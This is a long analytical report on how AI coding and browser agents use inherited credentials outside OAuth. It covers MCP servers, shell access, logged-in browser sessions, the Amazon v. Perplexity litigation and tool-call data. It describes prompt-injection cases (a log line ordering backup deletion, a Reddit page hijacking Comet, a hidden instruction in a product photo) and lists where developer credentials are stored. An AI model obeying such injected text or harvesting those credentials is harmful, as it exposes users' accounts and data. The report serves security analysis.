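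OX wanted Anthropic to fix this in the protocol and the kits, so that every product built on them would inherit the protection. flyingpenguin, whose author promotes his own competing product, lists four proposals. The kits would start only servers described in a manifest and would block high-risk commands by default. Developers would have to switch on a "dangerous mode" before using changeable arguments, and registries would require manifests signed by verified developers.

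Anthropic declined, replying that the design "does represent a secure default", and OX reports that it left developers to clean inputs. The makers of LangChain and FastMCP, two widely used toolkits, took much the same position. Cursor's makers pointed out that a user has to accept any edit to its configuration file.

The disagreement is mostly about whether the command in a configuration entry counts as trusted input. ARMO, another security vendor, accepts that the affected products had real bugs, but says OX's thesis amounts to observing that a configuration file has a field containing a command. ARMO has a point, because a program can't start a local server without running something. A list of allowed commands would not help much if it included `npx`, which can fetch and run almost any code. Flowise, a tool for building agents, had filtered its commands with such a list, and OX got past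 the filter in one step. flyingpenguin takes the bypass as evidence that developers can't solve the problem by themselves. The bypass also seems to count against OX's own proposal to block risky commands.

The dangerous-mode switch is harder to dismiss, because it would take an honest developer very little effort and might warn the makers of a web application that visitors' input could reach the command.

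Most of the changes have been made in individual products. When OX published, it listed patches for three of the ten vulnerabilities, those in LiteLLM, Bisheng and DocsGPT. According to flyingpenguin, Anthropic had updated its security documentation after OX's first report to recommend caution with stdio. The July 2026 specification still has the client launch the server as a subprocess, with no limit on which commands it may run. OX's proposals concern which code may start, and none would have added a service-side check. A server that passed all of them could still hold a static key for the user's whole account.

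### What the guidance asks of agent programs

The Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* treats installing a local server as running unknown code. Its firmest rules cover one-click installation, in which the agent program fills in the configuration for the user. Before running anything, the program must show the exact command in full, identify it as potentially dangerous, and get the user's explicit approval. It should also highlight risky patterns, such as commands that ask for administrator rights, and run the server in a sandbox with minimal access.

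An agent program that lacks the approval dialog departs from an accepted standard, while one that lacks a sandbox only ignores a recommendation. The dialog comes from *MCP Client Security Requirements for Local Server Installation* (Delimarsky, 2025), a proposal with final status on the project's standards track. Delimarsky says that clients "MUST" show the dialog, though he also calls the proposal a best practice. The sandbox is only a "SHOULD". The guidance page, Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* (2025), was part of the specification when the project published it in June 2025, but is now one of the tutorials. The stdio page of the July 2026 specification mentions neither measure.

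The protocol cannot enforce either measure. Delimarsky's proposal leaves MCP's messages unchanged, so a server cannot tell whether the user saw a dialog. The one-click rule also does not cover developers who edit the configuration file by hand. Delimarsky acknowledges that users may approve a malicious command despite the warning. Approval covers only the command that starts the server, and the dialog does not limit what the server can later do with its key.

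The project's maintainers have not finished working on these problems. The scope of the Model Context Protocol Security Interest Group includes handling secrets and isolating processes over stdio, because the HTTP authorization specification does not apply to stdio. It also includes how an agent program can verify the packages it starts.

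## Shell commands, file edits and command-line logins

A local MCP server offers the model a fixed list of tools, but coding agents also come with a shell that can start any program on the machine, and with tools that read and change files directly. The agent needs no separate key for any of these, and it can reach any logins the developer has saved.

### From a tool call to a running command

Claude Code's built-in tools include `Read`, `Edit`, `Write` and `Bash`. Bash is a common shell, a program that takes typed commands and starts other programs. To install a Python package, the model produces a tool call containing `{"command": "pip install requests"}`, an example from Anthropic's documentation. The agent program passes the command to a shell, which starts `pip`, and returns the output to the model as text. According to Anthropic's *Tools reference*, each command runs in a separate process,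 with the shortcuts from the user's shell startup file loaded.

Shell commands and file edits don't use MCP, because the agent program itself contains the code that carries them out. No server receives the tool call, so none can return a 401 response requiring a token.

File edits are just as direct. `Edit` replaces old text with new text, both supplied by the model. Claude Code normally requires that the model has read the file and that the old text matches exactly and appears only once. These checks catch mistakes, such as an edit based on an outdated copy, but they don't establish whether the user wanted the edit.

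Shell commands are harder to check than most other tool calls. A typed tool for closing an issue has separate fields for the repository and issue number, so software can test each value, but a shell command is one string that may start several programs. *Breaking Down Bash Commands in TraceLab* (Zhu, Jacob and colleagues, 2026) analyzes 158,610 shell calls from Claude and 264,670 from Codex. Claude's calls started an average of 5.62 programs each, and Codex's started 1.53. Many of these programs only searched or displayed files. Git made up 3.6% of the programs Claude started and 5.9% of those Codex started, while Python made up 3.7% and 10.0%. A command that starts Python may reveal very little about what it will do, since the script it runs could delete a folder or send a web request.

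Whether a change can be undone also depends on which tool made it. Claude Code takes a snapshot of files before each change so the user can restore them, but Anthropic warns that the snapshots only cover changes made with Claude Code's file editing tools. If a shell command overwrites a file, the user needs another backup to recover it.

### What the operating system checks

On Linux and macOS, each process inherits its user ID from the process that started it. If a developer starts Claude Code in a terminal, and Claude Code starts a shell that runs `rm` to delete a file, all three processes have the developer's ID. When one of them tries to open a file, the operating system compares the ID with the file's owner and permissions. A private SSH key, which developers use to log in to servers, typically has permissions that let its owner read it but no other ordinary account.

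These checks suit a shared computer. They stop the agent from reading a colleague's files, or from changing system files without administrator rights. But they cannot distinguish the agent from its user, because both have the same ID. A command that displays the SSH key makes the same request whether the developer typed it or the model produced it.

macOS adds some checks for each application, for example before an app can open the Documents folder. For an agent that runs in a terminal, the application is usually the terminal, so one approval covers the developer's commands and the agent's. The operating system can only treat the agent differently if someone first gives it a separate user account or puts it in a sandbox.

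### What a developer's account exposes

Command-line tools save their logins so that people don't have to log in for every command. A developer's account might hold all of the following:

| Credential | Usual place | What it allows |
|---|---|---|
| SSH keys | `~/.ssh` | Logging in to servers and uploading code |
| Cloud profiles | `~/.aws`, `~/.config/gcloud` | Whatever the developer's role permits in the company's cloud |
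| Package registry tokens | `~/.npmrc`, `~/.pypirc` | Publishing new versions of the developer's packages |
| Saved logins of tools such as `gh` | The system's credential store, or a file | Using the account within the token's scopes |
| Project secrets | `.env` files in project folders | Reaching databases and paid services |

Criminals already use malware to search for saved credentials. Winterford and colleagues cite Vidar Stealer on Windows and Atomic Stealer on macOS, which look through the folders where applications keep their data. A prompt injection could lead an agent to make the same search with ordinary commands.

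The agent often doesn't need to read a secret to use it. Once a developer unlocks a passphrase-protected SSH key, a background program will usually sign with it for any of the developer's processes. An encrypted credential store protects the `gh` token from someone who copies the disk, but it does little against an agent that can run `gh`, which fetches the token automatically. The agent can also print the token by running `gh auth token`.

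How much damage this could do depends on what the accounts behind the credentials can access. AWS, Amazon's cloud business, writes that without additional controls, developers often let agents use their administrator credentials, shared development roles or even production roles. Companies gave people such broad access assuming they would use judgment. An agent gets the same access without that human judgment, and works much faster.

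### How an agent uses a person's cloud login

Suppose a developer asks an agent why a nightly job in the company's AWS account failed.

1. That morning, for ordinary work, the developer ran `aws sso login`. A browser page opened, and the developer logged in and approved access for AWS's command-line tool. This was an OAuth login.
2. The tool saved the resulting token in a folder under `~/.aws`.
3. The model now produces the command `aws logs tail nightly-job --profile production`, and the agent program runs it.
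4. The `aws` program finds the saved token and exchanges it for temporary credentials for the role in the `production` profile. It signs the request with those.
5. AWS checks the signature and the role's permissions, and returns the logs. Its own records attribute the request to the developer's session.
6. One log line contains text that an outsider typed into a web form, with an instruction to delete the company's backups. If the model follows it, the next command uses the same login. AWS deletes the backups if the role permits that.

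Some limits still apply. If the role can only read, AWS refuses the deletion. The temporary credentials expire, and once the login itself expires, the developer has to approve a new one. The company can also set rules that apply to every role in its account.

As in the GitHub example, the developer approved the command-line tool, not the agent, so AWS cannot narrow or revoke the agent's access separately from the tool's.

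A second profile with a read-only role would help if the agent cannot reach the first one. If both are in the same folder, the agent can switch between them by changing one word in the command.

With `gh`, the main remaining limit is the token's scopes, which can build up over time. According to Arch Linux's manual page for `gh auth refresh`, the command keeps scopes the user added earlier unless they remove them. A developer who once added the `delete_repo` scope to clear out old projects may have forgotten it by the time an agent uses the token. A fine-grained token would be narrower, but GitHub advises care when logging in to `gh` with one because the token's limits may cause confusing behavior.

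### From local servers to command-line tools

Anthropic advises users to have Claude Code work with outside services through command-line tools such as `gh`, `aws` and `gcloud`, which it calls the most context-efficient way to do so. A model's context is the text it can take into account at once, and tool descriptions use some of it up. According to manveerc's *MCP vs. CLI for AI agents*, connecting a standard GitHub MCP server uses about 55,000 tokens (pieces of words) before the agent does anything useful.

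Models also already know the popular commands. A February post, reproduced in Conffab's *MCP is dead. Long live the CLI* (2026), attributes this to the manuals, forum answers and scripts in their training data. Shell commands can also pass their output to each other, which separate MCP tools can't do. Zechner (2025) argued that GitHub's MCP server mostly duplicates `gh` and often leads to much worse results, but he still saw a use for MCP where no convenient command-line tool exists.

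A skill is a set of written instructions, sometimes with scripts, that an agent loads when a task needs them. In Anthropic's *Extending Claude’s capabilities with skills and MCP servers*, an MCP server provides access to a system and a skill explains how to use it. A skill that explains how to use `gh` has no credential of its own, so the agent uses the existing login. Cloud providers now distribute skills themselves. In June, AWS (2026) added a command to its command-line tool that installs AWS's agent tools in Claude Code, Codex, Cursor and other coding agents, and added commands to find and manage skills.

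Anthropic's *Building agents that reach production systems with MCP* (2026) recommends command-line tools for local machines and sandboxed containers, where their login is "usually a credential file on disk". For agents that run in the cloud, it recommends remote MCP servers, partly because MCP standardizes the login. Anthropic expects mature services to offer a command-line tool, a remote MCP server and a direct API. Zhou, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers*, read this guidance as a shift in MCP's role towards remote services; that shift leaves local servers with fewer uses of their own.

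Some of these arguments against typed tools have good answers. *MCP is Dead; Long Live MCP!* (2026) points out that a company's custom command-line tool has the same context problem as MCP and lacks its structure. The model probably hasn't seen the tool in training, so it has to read the help text first. The 55,000-token figure is also less of a problem than it was. Anthropic reports that loading tool descriptions only when needed tends to cut the tokens they use by more than 85%, and that Cloudflare covers about 2,500 operations with two MCP tools and roughly 1,000 tokens.

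Large organizations have other reasons to keep MCP. *Skills, CLIs, and MCP* describes companies where one team runs the official servers and other teams build agents on top of them, so the company can govern access in one place. manveerc agrees that command-line tools are efficient but disputes the security argument for them, which is based on what works for a single developer.

The effect on OAuth depends on which kind of server the command-line tool replaces. A developer who switches from a local server with a static key to `gh` exchanges one inherited credential for another. This may improve security a little, because the token can move from a plaintext configuration file to an encrypted store. But the local server could have used a narrow token made only for the agent, and it offered a limited set of tools. If the tool replaces a remote server with its own OAuth grant, the service loses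 its only record of what the user allowed the agent program to do.

### How services try to recognize agents

AWS customers control access with policies that can test conditions on each request, and AWS has added two conditions for agents. One is true when the request came through an MCP server that AWS runs, and the other identifies which server it was. One of AWS's sample policies lets an agent read stored files through these servers but not delete them.

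AWS's own server attaches this information, so a misled model cannot remove it, but it is missing when the agent runs `aws s3 rm` in a shell. The AWS-run servers use the developer's existing AWS credentials, so a laptop that can use these servers can often make the direct call too. AWS also warns that older policies that block the server by denying the action `aws-mcp:InvokeMcp` no longer work, and that companies must rewrite them with the new conditions.

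To cover shell commands, the command-line tool itself has to report that an agent is using it. According to AWS News (2025), the coding assistant Amazon Q Developer adds a marker to the user agent string of its AWS commands, which is the text that identifies a program to a service. A company can write a policy that allows commands with this marker to read but not write.

The command-line tool of GitLab, another code host, labels requests from agents made by other companies. The tool, `glab`, checks for environment variables that Claude Code, Codex, Cursor and OpenCode set for the programs they start. *feat(api): detect coding agents in User-Agent header* gives `Coding-Agent/claude-code` as an example of the label. GitLab's server did not yet read the label when *Extract Coding-Agent token from glab User-Agent header for analytics* proposed using it for statistics. GitHub's tool has a similar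 field in the usage data that GitHub collects to improve the product. Users can turn this collection off.

These labels provide weak security. According to one answer in *IAM policy only allowed from Cloudshell?*, a thread on AWS's question site, callers can put anything in the user agent string, so it should not be used to keep out unauthorized parties. An agent could clear the variable before running `glab`, or send the token with a different program. A rule based on the label can still stop an honest mistake, such as a model deleting the wrong folder while tidying up. Such a rule is probably worth having, because agents don't usually hide what they are.

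*Agent attribution via Trusted Identity Propagation* (Steele, 2026) uses the same openness to improve AWS's logs. Claude Code, for example, sets a variable with the session's ID. In Steele's design, the company's login system adds the agent's name and session to the token it issues, and a recent AWS feature carries those details into the audit log. An administrator could then trace a deleted file to one conversation. The laptop still has to prove to the login system that the request comes from an agent, which is difficult when the agent and the developer run under the same account.

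On December 1, 2026, AWS announced a more thorough change that gives agents separate identities. *AWS 強化雲端資安 讓 AI Agent 擁有獨立身分憑證* (林, 2026) reports that the preview compares a running program's environment with a template and then issues the program its own short-lived credential. The built-in support covers two hosting environments, Amazon's Kubernetes service and its AgentCore platform for agents. An agent in a developer's terminal would still use the developer's login unless someone set up another arrangement. A separate identity also doesn't narrow an agent's permissions by itself. KBY Technologies' *AWS IAM for Agents, Bedrock Gateway and Greenlight* cautions that an agent running under a broad role can do everything the role allows.

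## Browser agents that act in the user's logged-in sessions

A browser agent can use almost any website that a person can, including sites with no API, MCP server or command-line tool. It reads pages and presses buttons in a browser. If the user is logged in there, the agent inherits the user's credential, usually a session cookie, and the site treats the agent's actions as the user's.

### How a cookie keeps a user logged in

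Web servers handle each request separately, so without some kind of reminder a site would have to ask for the password on every page. When a user logs in, the site creates a session, which is a record on its own machines that links a long random string to the user's account. It sends the string to the browser in a header like this one:

```
Set-Cookie: session=8f3ac1...; Secure; HttpOnly
```

The browser stores this cookie and attaches it to every later request to the site. The site looks up the string to find the account and serves the request as the account's user. This continues until the user logs out, the session expires or someone revokes it.

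Like most OAuth tokens, an ordinary cookie works for whoever holds it, but the two settings in the example give some protection. `Secure` keeps the cookie off unencrypted connections, and `HttpOnly` stops scripts on the page from reading it. Neither affects a browser agent, because the browser attaches the cookie when the agent clicks a link, and the agent never needs to read it.

### Where the agent runs

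Some browsers have a built-in agent. Perplexity's Comet and OpenAI's ChatGPT Atlas show it in a panel next to the page. The model usually runs on a provider's servers, as Educated Guesswork's *Notes on Amazon v. Perplexity* explains, so the browser sends most of what the agent reads to the provider, though the cookies can stay on the user's machine. A site has little basis for telling the agent from the user if the agent shares the cookies, passwords and stored data of the user's ordinary browsing, but an agent that shares none of these looks like a separate visitor.

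An agent installed as a browser extension works in the user's open tabs and active sessions, and it inherits the permissions the user has given to particular sites. *Mind the Web* (Shapira, Gandhi and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a user who once allowed Google Meet to use the camera. A prompt injection could make the agent join a meeting with the camera on.

A hosted browser runs on the provider's machines and starts without the user's cookies or files. The user logs in to sites inside it, and some hosted agents, such as OpenAI's Operator, can keep those logins for later tasks. The provider then holds the session cookies, and the sites receive requests from the provider's network. The user has to trust the provider more, but the agent has only the logins the user chose to give it.

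Shapira and colleagues also describe an agent that opens a fresh browser on the user's own computer. The browser starts logged out of every site but can still reach local files, and the user can log in to a site when a task requires it.

### One purchase through Comet

Suppose a user who is logged in to Amazon asks Comet to buy the cheapest phone charger with good reviews. An appeals court examined how Comet works in a lawsuit between Amazon and Perplexity, and Rijo (2026), in *Amazon loses injunction blocking Perplexity's AI shopping agent*, summarizes its description. The purchase would go roughly like this:

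1. The browser requests a page of search results from Amazon, with the user's cookie attached, and displays it.
2. The assistant takes a screenshot and sends it to Perplexity's servers along with the user's instructions.
3. The servers send back a navigation instruction, such as to open the third result. The browser requests that page, again with the cookie.
4. Steps 2 and 3 repeat until the assistant presses the order button. Amazon charges the saved card and ships the charger to the saved address.

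Amazon receives a series of page requests from the user's own network address, all with a valid cookie. Perplexity's servers never contact Amazon's directly, according to the *Brief of Amici Curiae Electronic Frontier Foundation, Alliance for Responsible Data Collection* (2026), which EFF, a digital rights group, filed with Mozilla and others in the case. Amazon can't check the order against the user's original instruction, which goes to Perplexity.

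A seller might hide an instruction to AI shopping agents in a product photo. According to Educated Guesswork, such attacks are hard to prevent in the browser because the agent has to read product pages to do its job. If the attack works, Amazon receives an order for a $90 charger that looks as valid as one for the $9 charger the user wanted. Similarly, when an agent types an email in a webmail page and presses "Send", the mail provider receives a message from a logged-in user.

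### Why the same-origin policy does not contain the agent

Browsers have long enforced the same-origin policy, which prevents a script from one origin from reading data that belongs to another. *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, 2026) defines an origin as the combination of a page's scheme (such as `http` or `https`), host name and port number. All three have to match, so `www.example.com` and `example.com` are different origins. Without this policy, a script on any blog could read the user's balance from a bank page in another tab.

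The same-origin policy restricts scripts but not users. A user can read their bank balance and type it into a blog comment. A browser agent uses the same text boxes and buttons, so the browser lets it do the same. The agent keeps what it reads on one page in its history and can write it on the next.

Wang and colleagues show that this can happen without an attacker. If a page displays part of another site in a frame and the user asks the agent to type a summary of the page into a text box, the agent may include the framed content. The outer page then receives text that its own scripts could not have read. An attacker can also use a prompt injection on a second page as a plain-language script, instructing the agent to write down what it saw on the first.

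The team tested five agentic browsers and six models with 50 combinations of page types. Data crossed between origins at what they call non-trivial rates, both with and without an attack. Most of the test pages were synthetic, so the rates may differ on real sites. Educated Guesswork describes a demonstration on a real product, Comet, by Brave, which makes a competing browser. A user asked Comet to summarize a Reddit page. Text planted on the page led the agent to give an attacker access to the user's Perplexity account and to email from Gmail, which an ordinary script on Reddit could not have read.

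Shapira and colleagues tested four agents with planted instructions disguised as helpful guidance for the user's task, and the attacks succeeded 80% to 100% of the time. The models are now well over a year old, so these rates are a poor guide to current models. A better model is less likely to follow the planted text, but the gap in the same-origin policy doesn't depend on the model, and the browser would still let the agent carry data from one site to another.

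Browser makers can't simply apply the same-origin policy to agents, because it would block transfers that users often want, such as copying a flight number from an email into an airline's form. Wang and colleagues propose that the browser track where data came from and ask the user before it goes to a different origin. Users can also limit the damage by giving the agent a separate browser profile with only the logins it needs.

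### What the site can still check

The site still applies the user's permissions to each request, so an agent can't spend from a stranger's account. Many sites also check for stolen passwords and cookies and for unwanted bots. Some of these checks can stop an agent, but they reveal little about what it is doing.

Before a sensitive action, such as changing a password or adding a payee, a site may ask the user to log in again. An agent without the password has to wait for the user. This protection is lost if the user has given the agent the password or lets the browser fill it in automatically.

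A passkey, which is a private key that the user's device or password manager holds for one site, provides a stronger check. The site sends a random challenge, the user normally unlocks the key with a fingerprint or PIN, and the device signs the challenge. The agent can't provide a fingerprint, so a successful check is good evidence that a person was involved.

A fresh login doesn't necessarily show that the user agreed to the agent's action. An ordinary passkey signature covers the site's challenge but not the details of a payment, so a user might approve what looks like a routine login after the agent has entered the wrong payee. A bank app that shows the amount and payee on the user's phone gives better evidence, because the user approves that specific payment. Many sites also don't ask for another login for some time after a fresh one, and the agent can act in the session during that period.

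Malware can copy an ordinary cookie to another computer and use the session there. A site can prevent this by binding its cookies to the user's device. The browser creates a private key that stays on the machine, ideally in a security chip, and the site issues short-lived cookies that it renews only if the browser proves it still has the key. An agent in the user's own browser passes this check automatically because it runs on the same machine. The check stops a provider from copying the user's cookies into a hosted browser, but if the user logs in inside the hosted browser instead, that browser can have its own key.

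**Bot detection.** Sites also look for signs of automation, such as requests from a data center, unusual timing or mouse movements, and small differences in browser behavior. They may respond with a challenge meant to be easy for people and hard for software. Cloudflare's *Perplexity is using stealth, undeclared crawlers to evade website no-crawl directives* reports that the company's detection system identified all the undeclared crawling it had observed as bot traffic, and that the crawlers failed its challenges. Cloudflare sells this system, and crawlers that collect pages in bulk are probably easier to catch than an agent in a customer's own browser. Comet uses the customer's own network address and cookie, so the site has only behavior and technical details to check.

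Comet uses the same user agent string as Chrome. Amazon calls this a disguise, but Educated Guesswork points out that Chrome's own string also contains the names "Mozilla" and "Safari". Sites have often withheld features from browsers they did not recognize, so new browsers copy the strings of established ones.

Amazon has managed to detect browser agents, at least for a while. But even perfect detection would only show that software is operating the browser. Without the user's instructions, the site could block all agents or none, but it couldn't tell which orders the user never wanted.

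### Amazon v. Perplexity

With OAuth, a program needs permission from both the service and the user to use an account. A browser agent can use the account with only the user's permission. The lawsuit *Amazon.com Services v. Perplexity AI* is about whether the site can require its own permission too.

#### What each side argues

In *Demand to Cease and Desist* (Kaba, 2025), Amazon's lawyer wrote in October 2025 that Perplexity had placed orders for customers in 2024 through a few Amazon accounts that it managed itself, and had agreed to stop when Amazon objected. In August 2025, Amazon noticed Comet working inside customers' own accounts. According to the complaint quoted in PPC Land's *Amazon sues Perplexity over covert AI agent access to marketplace*, Amazon put up a technical barrier on August 19, and within 24 hours Perplexity released a version that got past it.

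Amazon wants agents to identify themselves and to stay away if it doesn't want them. In its public statement, Amazon compares Comet to a food delivery app, which should respect a restaurant's decision not to take part. Kaba adds that Comet is vulnerable to prompt injection and can give customers a worse deal, for example by not offering to add a product to an existing delivery.

Perplexity sees the assistant as the user's own tool. In a blog post reproduced by Sneos (2025), the company argued that an assistant "must be indistinguishable from you" and acts with the user's credentials, permissions and rights. According to Digital Commerce 360 (2025), Perplexity also said that Comet keeps logins only on the user's device and that Amazon mostly wants to keep showing people ads.

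Educated Guesswork, whose author used to work at Mozilla, sides with users who want to control their own browsing. The post argues that Amazon's interests differ from its customers', since sellers pay for prominent places in search results. The author also doubts that security alone explains the lawsuit, because flaws in ordinary browsers can do just as much harm. Amazon forbids apps that use its affiliate API from imitating its shopping app, and the author knows of no outside storefront that can place orders there. If that is right, users who want an assistant to shop on Amazon cannot choose OAuth instead, because Amazon offers no OAuth grant for placing orders.

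Perplexity seems right that users should be able to choose an assistant, but they can do that even if the site can tell the assistant from a person. If the site can't tell them apart, it also can't enforce limits that users might want on the assistant. Amazon could not offer a $50 spending cap for agents, for example, if it could not tell which orders came from them. Amazon therefore has a stronger case for requiring agents to identify themselves than for being allowed to block them, though in practice identification makes blocking much easier.

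#### What the courts decided

Amazon sued Perplexity in November 2025. On March 9, 2026, a district judge ordered Perplexity to stop Comet from making purchases on Amazon while the case continued, according to Bloomberg Law's *Amazon Wins Court Order Blocking Perplexity’s AI Shopping Bots* (2026). About a week later, the Ninth Circuit, the federal appeals court for the western United States, paused the order, as Law360 reported. The appeals court threw the order out on August 4.

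The decision depended on who "accesses" Amazon's computers. The Computer Fraud and Abuse Act, the main federal law against hacking, applies to whoever intentionally accesses a computer without authorization. The judges held that Comet's assistant is a tool and that the person using it is the one who accesses Amazon. They held that Perplexity did not enter Amazon's servers merely by receiving screenshots and sending back instructions. Amazon's claim under California's computer crime law failed for the same reason.

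Amazon had relied on an earlier case in which the same court held the company Power Ventures liable for continuing to access Facebook after Facebook blocked it and sent a warning letter. McCarthy (2026), in *Ninth Circuit Lifts Restrictions on Agentic AI Accessing Amazon*, explains that the judges considered that case different because Comet's users reach Amazon through their own computers. The judges were also concerned that Amazon's reading of the law could make ordinary users criminally liable for using an agent.

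The ruling is narrow. It concerns a temporary order, so the judges decided only that Amazon was unlikely to win on these claims, given the evidence so far. They left open whether Perplexity could be liable under other laws, and noted in a footnote that Amazon can still regulate access through its terms of service. The reasoning may not extend to hosted browsers, because there the agent company's own machine sends the requests, which looks much more like access by the company.

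In comments published with McCarthy's article, the law professor Eric Goldman expects courts to look closely at how much a software maker does to help its users. If it helps enough, the maker may become the one legally responsible, but nobody yet knows how much help that takes. He also asks whether Amazon could now sue the users themselves.

#### The position in December 2026

On September 10, the appeals court left its ruling in place despite a further request from Amazon, according to MediaPost's *Appeals Court Again Rejects Amazon Bid To Block Perplexity* (2026). Amazon then turned to contract law and technical blocks. Constantin (2026), in *Amazon blocks Muse and takes Perplexity back to court*, reports that Amazon filed an amended complaint on September 21 accusing Perplexity of misleading the appeals court. This could matter a lot if Amazon can prove it, because the judges limited their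 decision to the facts before them.

Amazon has started blocking Muse, an assistant from Meta. Users saw a message that an unauthorized AI agent violates the conditions they had agreed to. Amazon objects that Muse does not identify itself and appears to store customers' credentials. Meta says that Muse uses passwords from secure storage and can't see them. Amazon also plans to block agents from Google and OpenAI, according to TechSpot's *Amazon is blocking Meta's shopping AI agent* (2026).

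As of early December, the amended complaint is the latest reported step in the Perplexity case. For now, a user's permission is probably enough under federal hacking law in the Ninth Circuit if the agent runs on the user's own machine. Amazon can still forbid agents in its terms and block the ones it detects. The courts have not decided whether Perplexity or its users owe Amazon anything for breaking those terms.

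### Signed requests and the reasons not to sign

Web Bot Auth is a proposed standard that lets an agent identify itself to websites with a cryptographic signature. The agent's operator creates a pair of keys and publishes the public one at a web address. The agent uses the private key to sign parts of each request, such as the name of the site and the time, and the site fetches the public key to check the signature. A signature is much harder to fake than a user agent string such as Chrome's, which anyone can copy, because only someone with the private key can produce a valid one. Each signature also has a time limit, which makes old signatures hard to reuse.

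If an agent in a logged-in session signed its requests, the site would receive both the user's cookie and the operator's signature. It could then log the agent's actions separately, refuse to let agents change passwords, or ask the user to confirm larger orders. These rules would restore some of what a separate OAuth grant provides, but each site would have to build them itself. The signature contains nothing about the user's task, so the site would still lack the list of permitted actions that the service in Hossen's experiments had.

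Signing is easiest for hosted browsers, because the operator can keep the private key on its own servers. If a browser on the user's laptop contained the key, other people could extract it and sign requests from their own software. The operator could instead sign the laptop's requests on its servers, but it would then learn which pages the agent requests.

Cloudflare reports that OpenAI's ChatGPT Agent signs its requests with Web Bot Auth. Amazon says that Comet and Muse have not even identified themselves by name. Their makers have a reason not to sign requests, since a signature gives a site a simple and reliable way to block an agent. Amazon's reported plan to block OpenAI's agents suggests that signing does little to make Amazon accept an agent. Similarly, some sites used to treat browsers worse when their user agent strings identified them accurately, so browser makers changed the strings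 to imitate other browsers.

Sites could give agents a reason to sign their requests, such as fewer bot challenges or permission to do routine tasks. A small shop that wants more orders has good reason to offer this, but a large marketplace that earns money from ads has less reason because an agent can skip the sponsored products.

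## How much of real agent use lies outside OAuth

No published study directly measures how much agent activity lies outside OAuth enforcement. A researcher would need to know, for every request, which credential the agent used and which program the user had approved to use it. Logs of tool calls rarely contain that information, and services often can't detect that a request comes from an agent. The available figures come from tool logs, internet scans and download counts, and each covers only part of the question.

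The answer also depends on what one counts. Suppose a developer's agent reads 200 files, runs 100 shell commands and then closes one issue through a remote MCP server that uses OAuth. 300 of the 301 tool calls are outside OAuth enforcement, but a count of MCP servers would find none outside it, because the only server in use has OAuth. A count of organizations would show that the developer's company has agent activity both inside and outside OAuth enforcement.

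At least 95% of tool calls by coding agents on developers' machines probably fall outside OAuth, though most of these calls never leave the machine. About 70% of the remote MCP servers found in the largest internet scan did not use OAuth. For agent use as a whole, the data support only an estimate with a very wide range.

### What coding agents call

The best data is on coding agents, because they keep detailed logs. *TraceLab*, by Zhu, Jacob and colleagues, analyzes 432,510 tool calls that Claude Code and Codex made between September 2025 and June 2026. The sessions came from 43 developers, and the team describes them as its own daily use of the agents, mainly to build and evaluate research systems. These developers may connect their agents to fewer business services than a company's staff would.

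*Agentic Coding in the Wild* (Liu, Qiu and colleagues, 2026) uses a much larger sample, Microsoft's records of GitHub Copilot's coding agent in the code editors Visual Studio and VS Code. The records cover 13.5 million sessions, 3.2 million users and 774.7 million tool calls in the United States during the first week of June 2026. The most common tool, `get_file`, made up 35.0% of calls. Terminal commands made up 17.0%, and a tool that replaces text in a file made up 9.8%.

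Some coding agents run on a cloud machine instead of the developer's own. *AgentLogs* (2026) collects 28.5 million tool calls by cloud agents on GitHub. Nearly all the runs (98.8%) used Copilot's agent, so the dataset is weak evidence about competing agents.

The table groups each dataset's tools by what they do. In the first three columns, each group's share is the sum of the published shares of its tools.

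| Kind of tool | Claude Code (Zhu and colleagues) | Codex (Zhu and colleagues) | Copilot in an editor (Liu and colleagues) | Cloud agents (*AgentLogs*) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Reading, searching and editing files and code | 41% | 8% | 71% | 40% |
| Shell commands and builds | 47% | 91% | 22% | 37% |
| Planning, setup and progress | 5% | Under 1% | 2% | 14% |
| Web pages and web search | 2% | Not listed | Not listed | Not listed |
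| Everything else, including any MCP tools | 4% | Under 1% | 5% | 9% |

The columns differ partly because the agents have different tools. Codex has no separate tool for reading a file, so it reads files with shell commands. Copilot has several file and search tools, so it needs the shell less often.

Only the last row is likely to contain calls inside OAuth enforcement, because calls to remote MCP servers would appear there, so its share is a rough upper limit. In the data from Zhu and colleagues, MCP tools account for at most 2.7% of Claude's calls and less than 0.1% of Codex's, or about 1% of all calls. Even if all of those went to remote servers with their own OAuth grants, about 99% of these developers' tool calls would still be outside OAuth enforcement.

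The same reasoning gives a limit of about 5% for Copilot. Liu and colleagues put 4.6% of calls in a group called "Others", which they describe as mostly customized tools. This limit is less certain because the records contain only about 45 different tools for 3.2 million users, which seems too few if each MCP tool appeared under its own name. Microsoft's records may combine custom tools under one label or leave some out.

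The cloud agents are harder to classify. About 3.8% of their calls are operations on GitHub, such as reading issues and posting comments. A cloud agent doesn't normally start with a developer's saved logins, and it may have a token that GitHub issued for the agent alone. If so, GitHub could limit the agent separately from the developer, even when the agent runs `git push` in its shell. Moving an agent to the cloud may therefore put more of its calls under separate limits, even if it uses the same tools.

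A newer version of the University of Washington data, on the project's website, SyFI TraceLab, covers 743,819 tool calls. Claude's three most common tools, `Bash`, `Read` and `Edit`, run commands and work on files, and they make up 85.0% of its calls. Codex's three most common tools make up 85.3% of its calls: `exec_command`, which starts a command; `write_stdin`, which continues or waits for one that is already running; and `exec`.

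The 85% figure shows how concentrated tool use is, not what share of it is outside OAuth. Most of the other 15% is probably outside OAuth too, since it includes tools for writing files and updating task lists. It is also unclear what `exec` does in this data. The project doesn't count it as a shell command, and without it the other two Codex tools make up about 75% of calls.

### How many of these calls reach a service

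Most of the calls in the table are outside OAuth because they involve no service. The share of calls that reach a service with an inherited credential matters more for the user's accounts. Nobody seems to have published that figure, but the shell data allow a partial answer.

According to SyFI TraceLab, 56.9% of the tool calls start a shell command. These commands started about 1.3 million programs. The most common was `echo`, at 18.1%, which agents mainly use to print progress messages. Five programs that search text or display parts of it (`grep`, `sed`, `head`, `tail` and `rg`) made up another 32.8%, so about half of the programs did little more than display or search text.

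Git is the most obvious candidate for reaching a service, because it can upload code with the user's saved key. It makes up 5.9% of the programs that Codex starts, or about 24,000 starts. Even if each came from a different tool call, only about 5% of Codex's calls would involve Git. The share that reaches a code host is probably much lower, since commands that show the history or the latest changes use only the local copy.

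The public data can't separate the two. To protect privacy, the project removed the arguments from each command, so `git status` and `git push` look the same. It also replaced the names of less common programs with labels. The hidden names include Modal, a cloud computing platform, but together they make up less than 1% of program starts.

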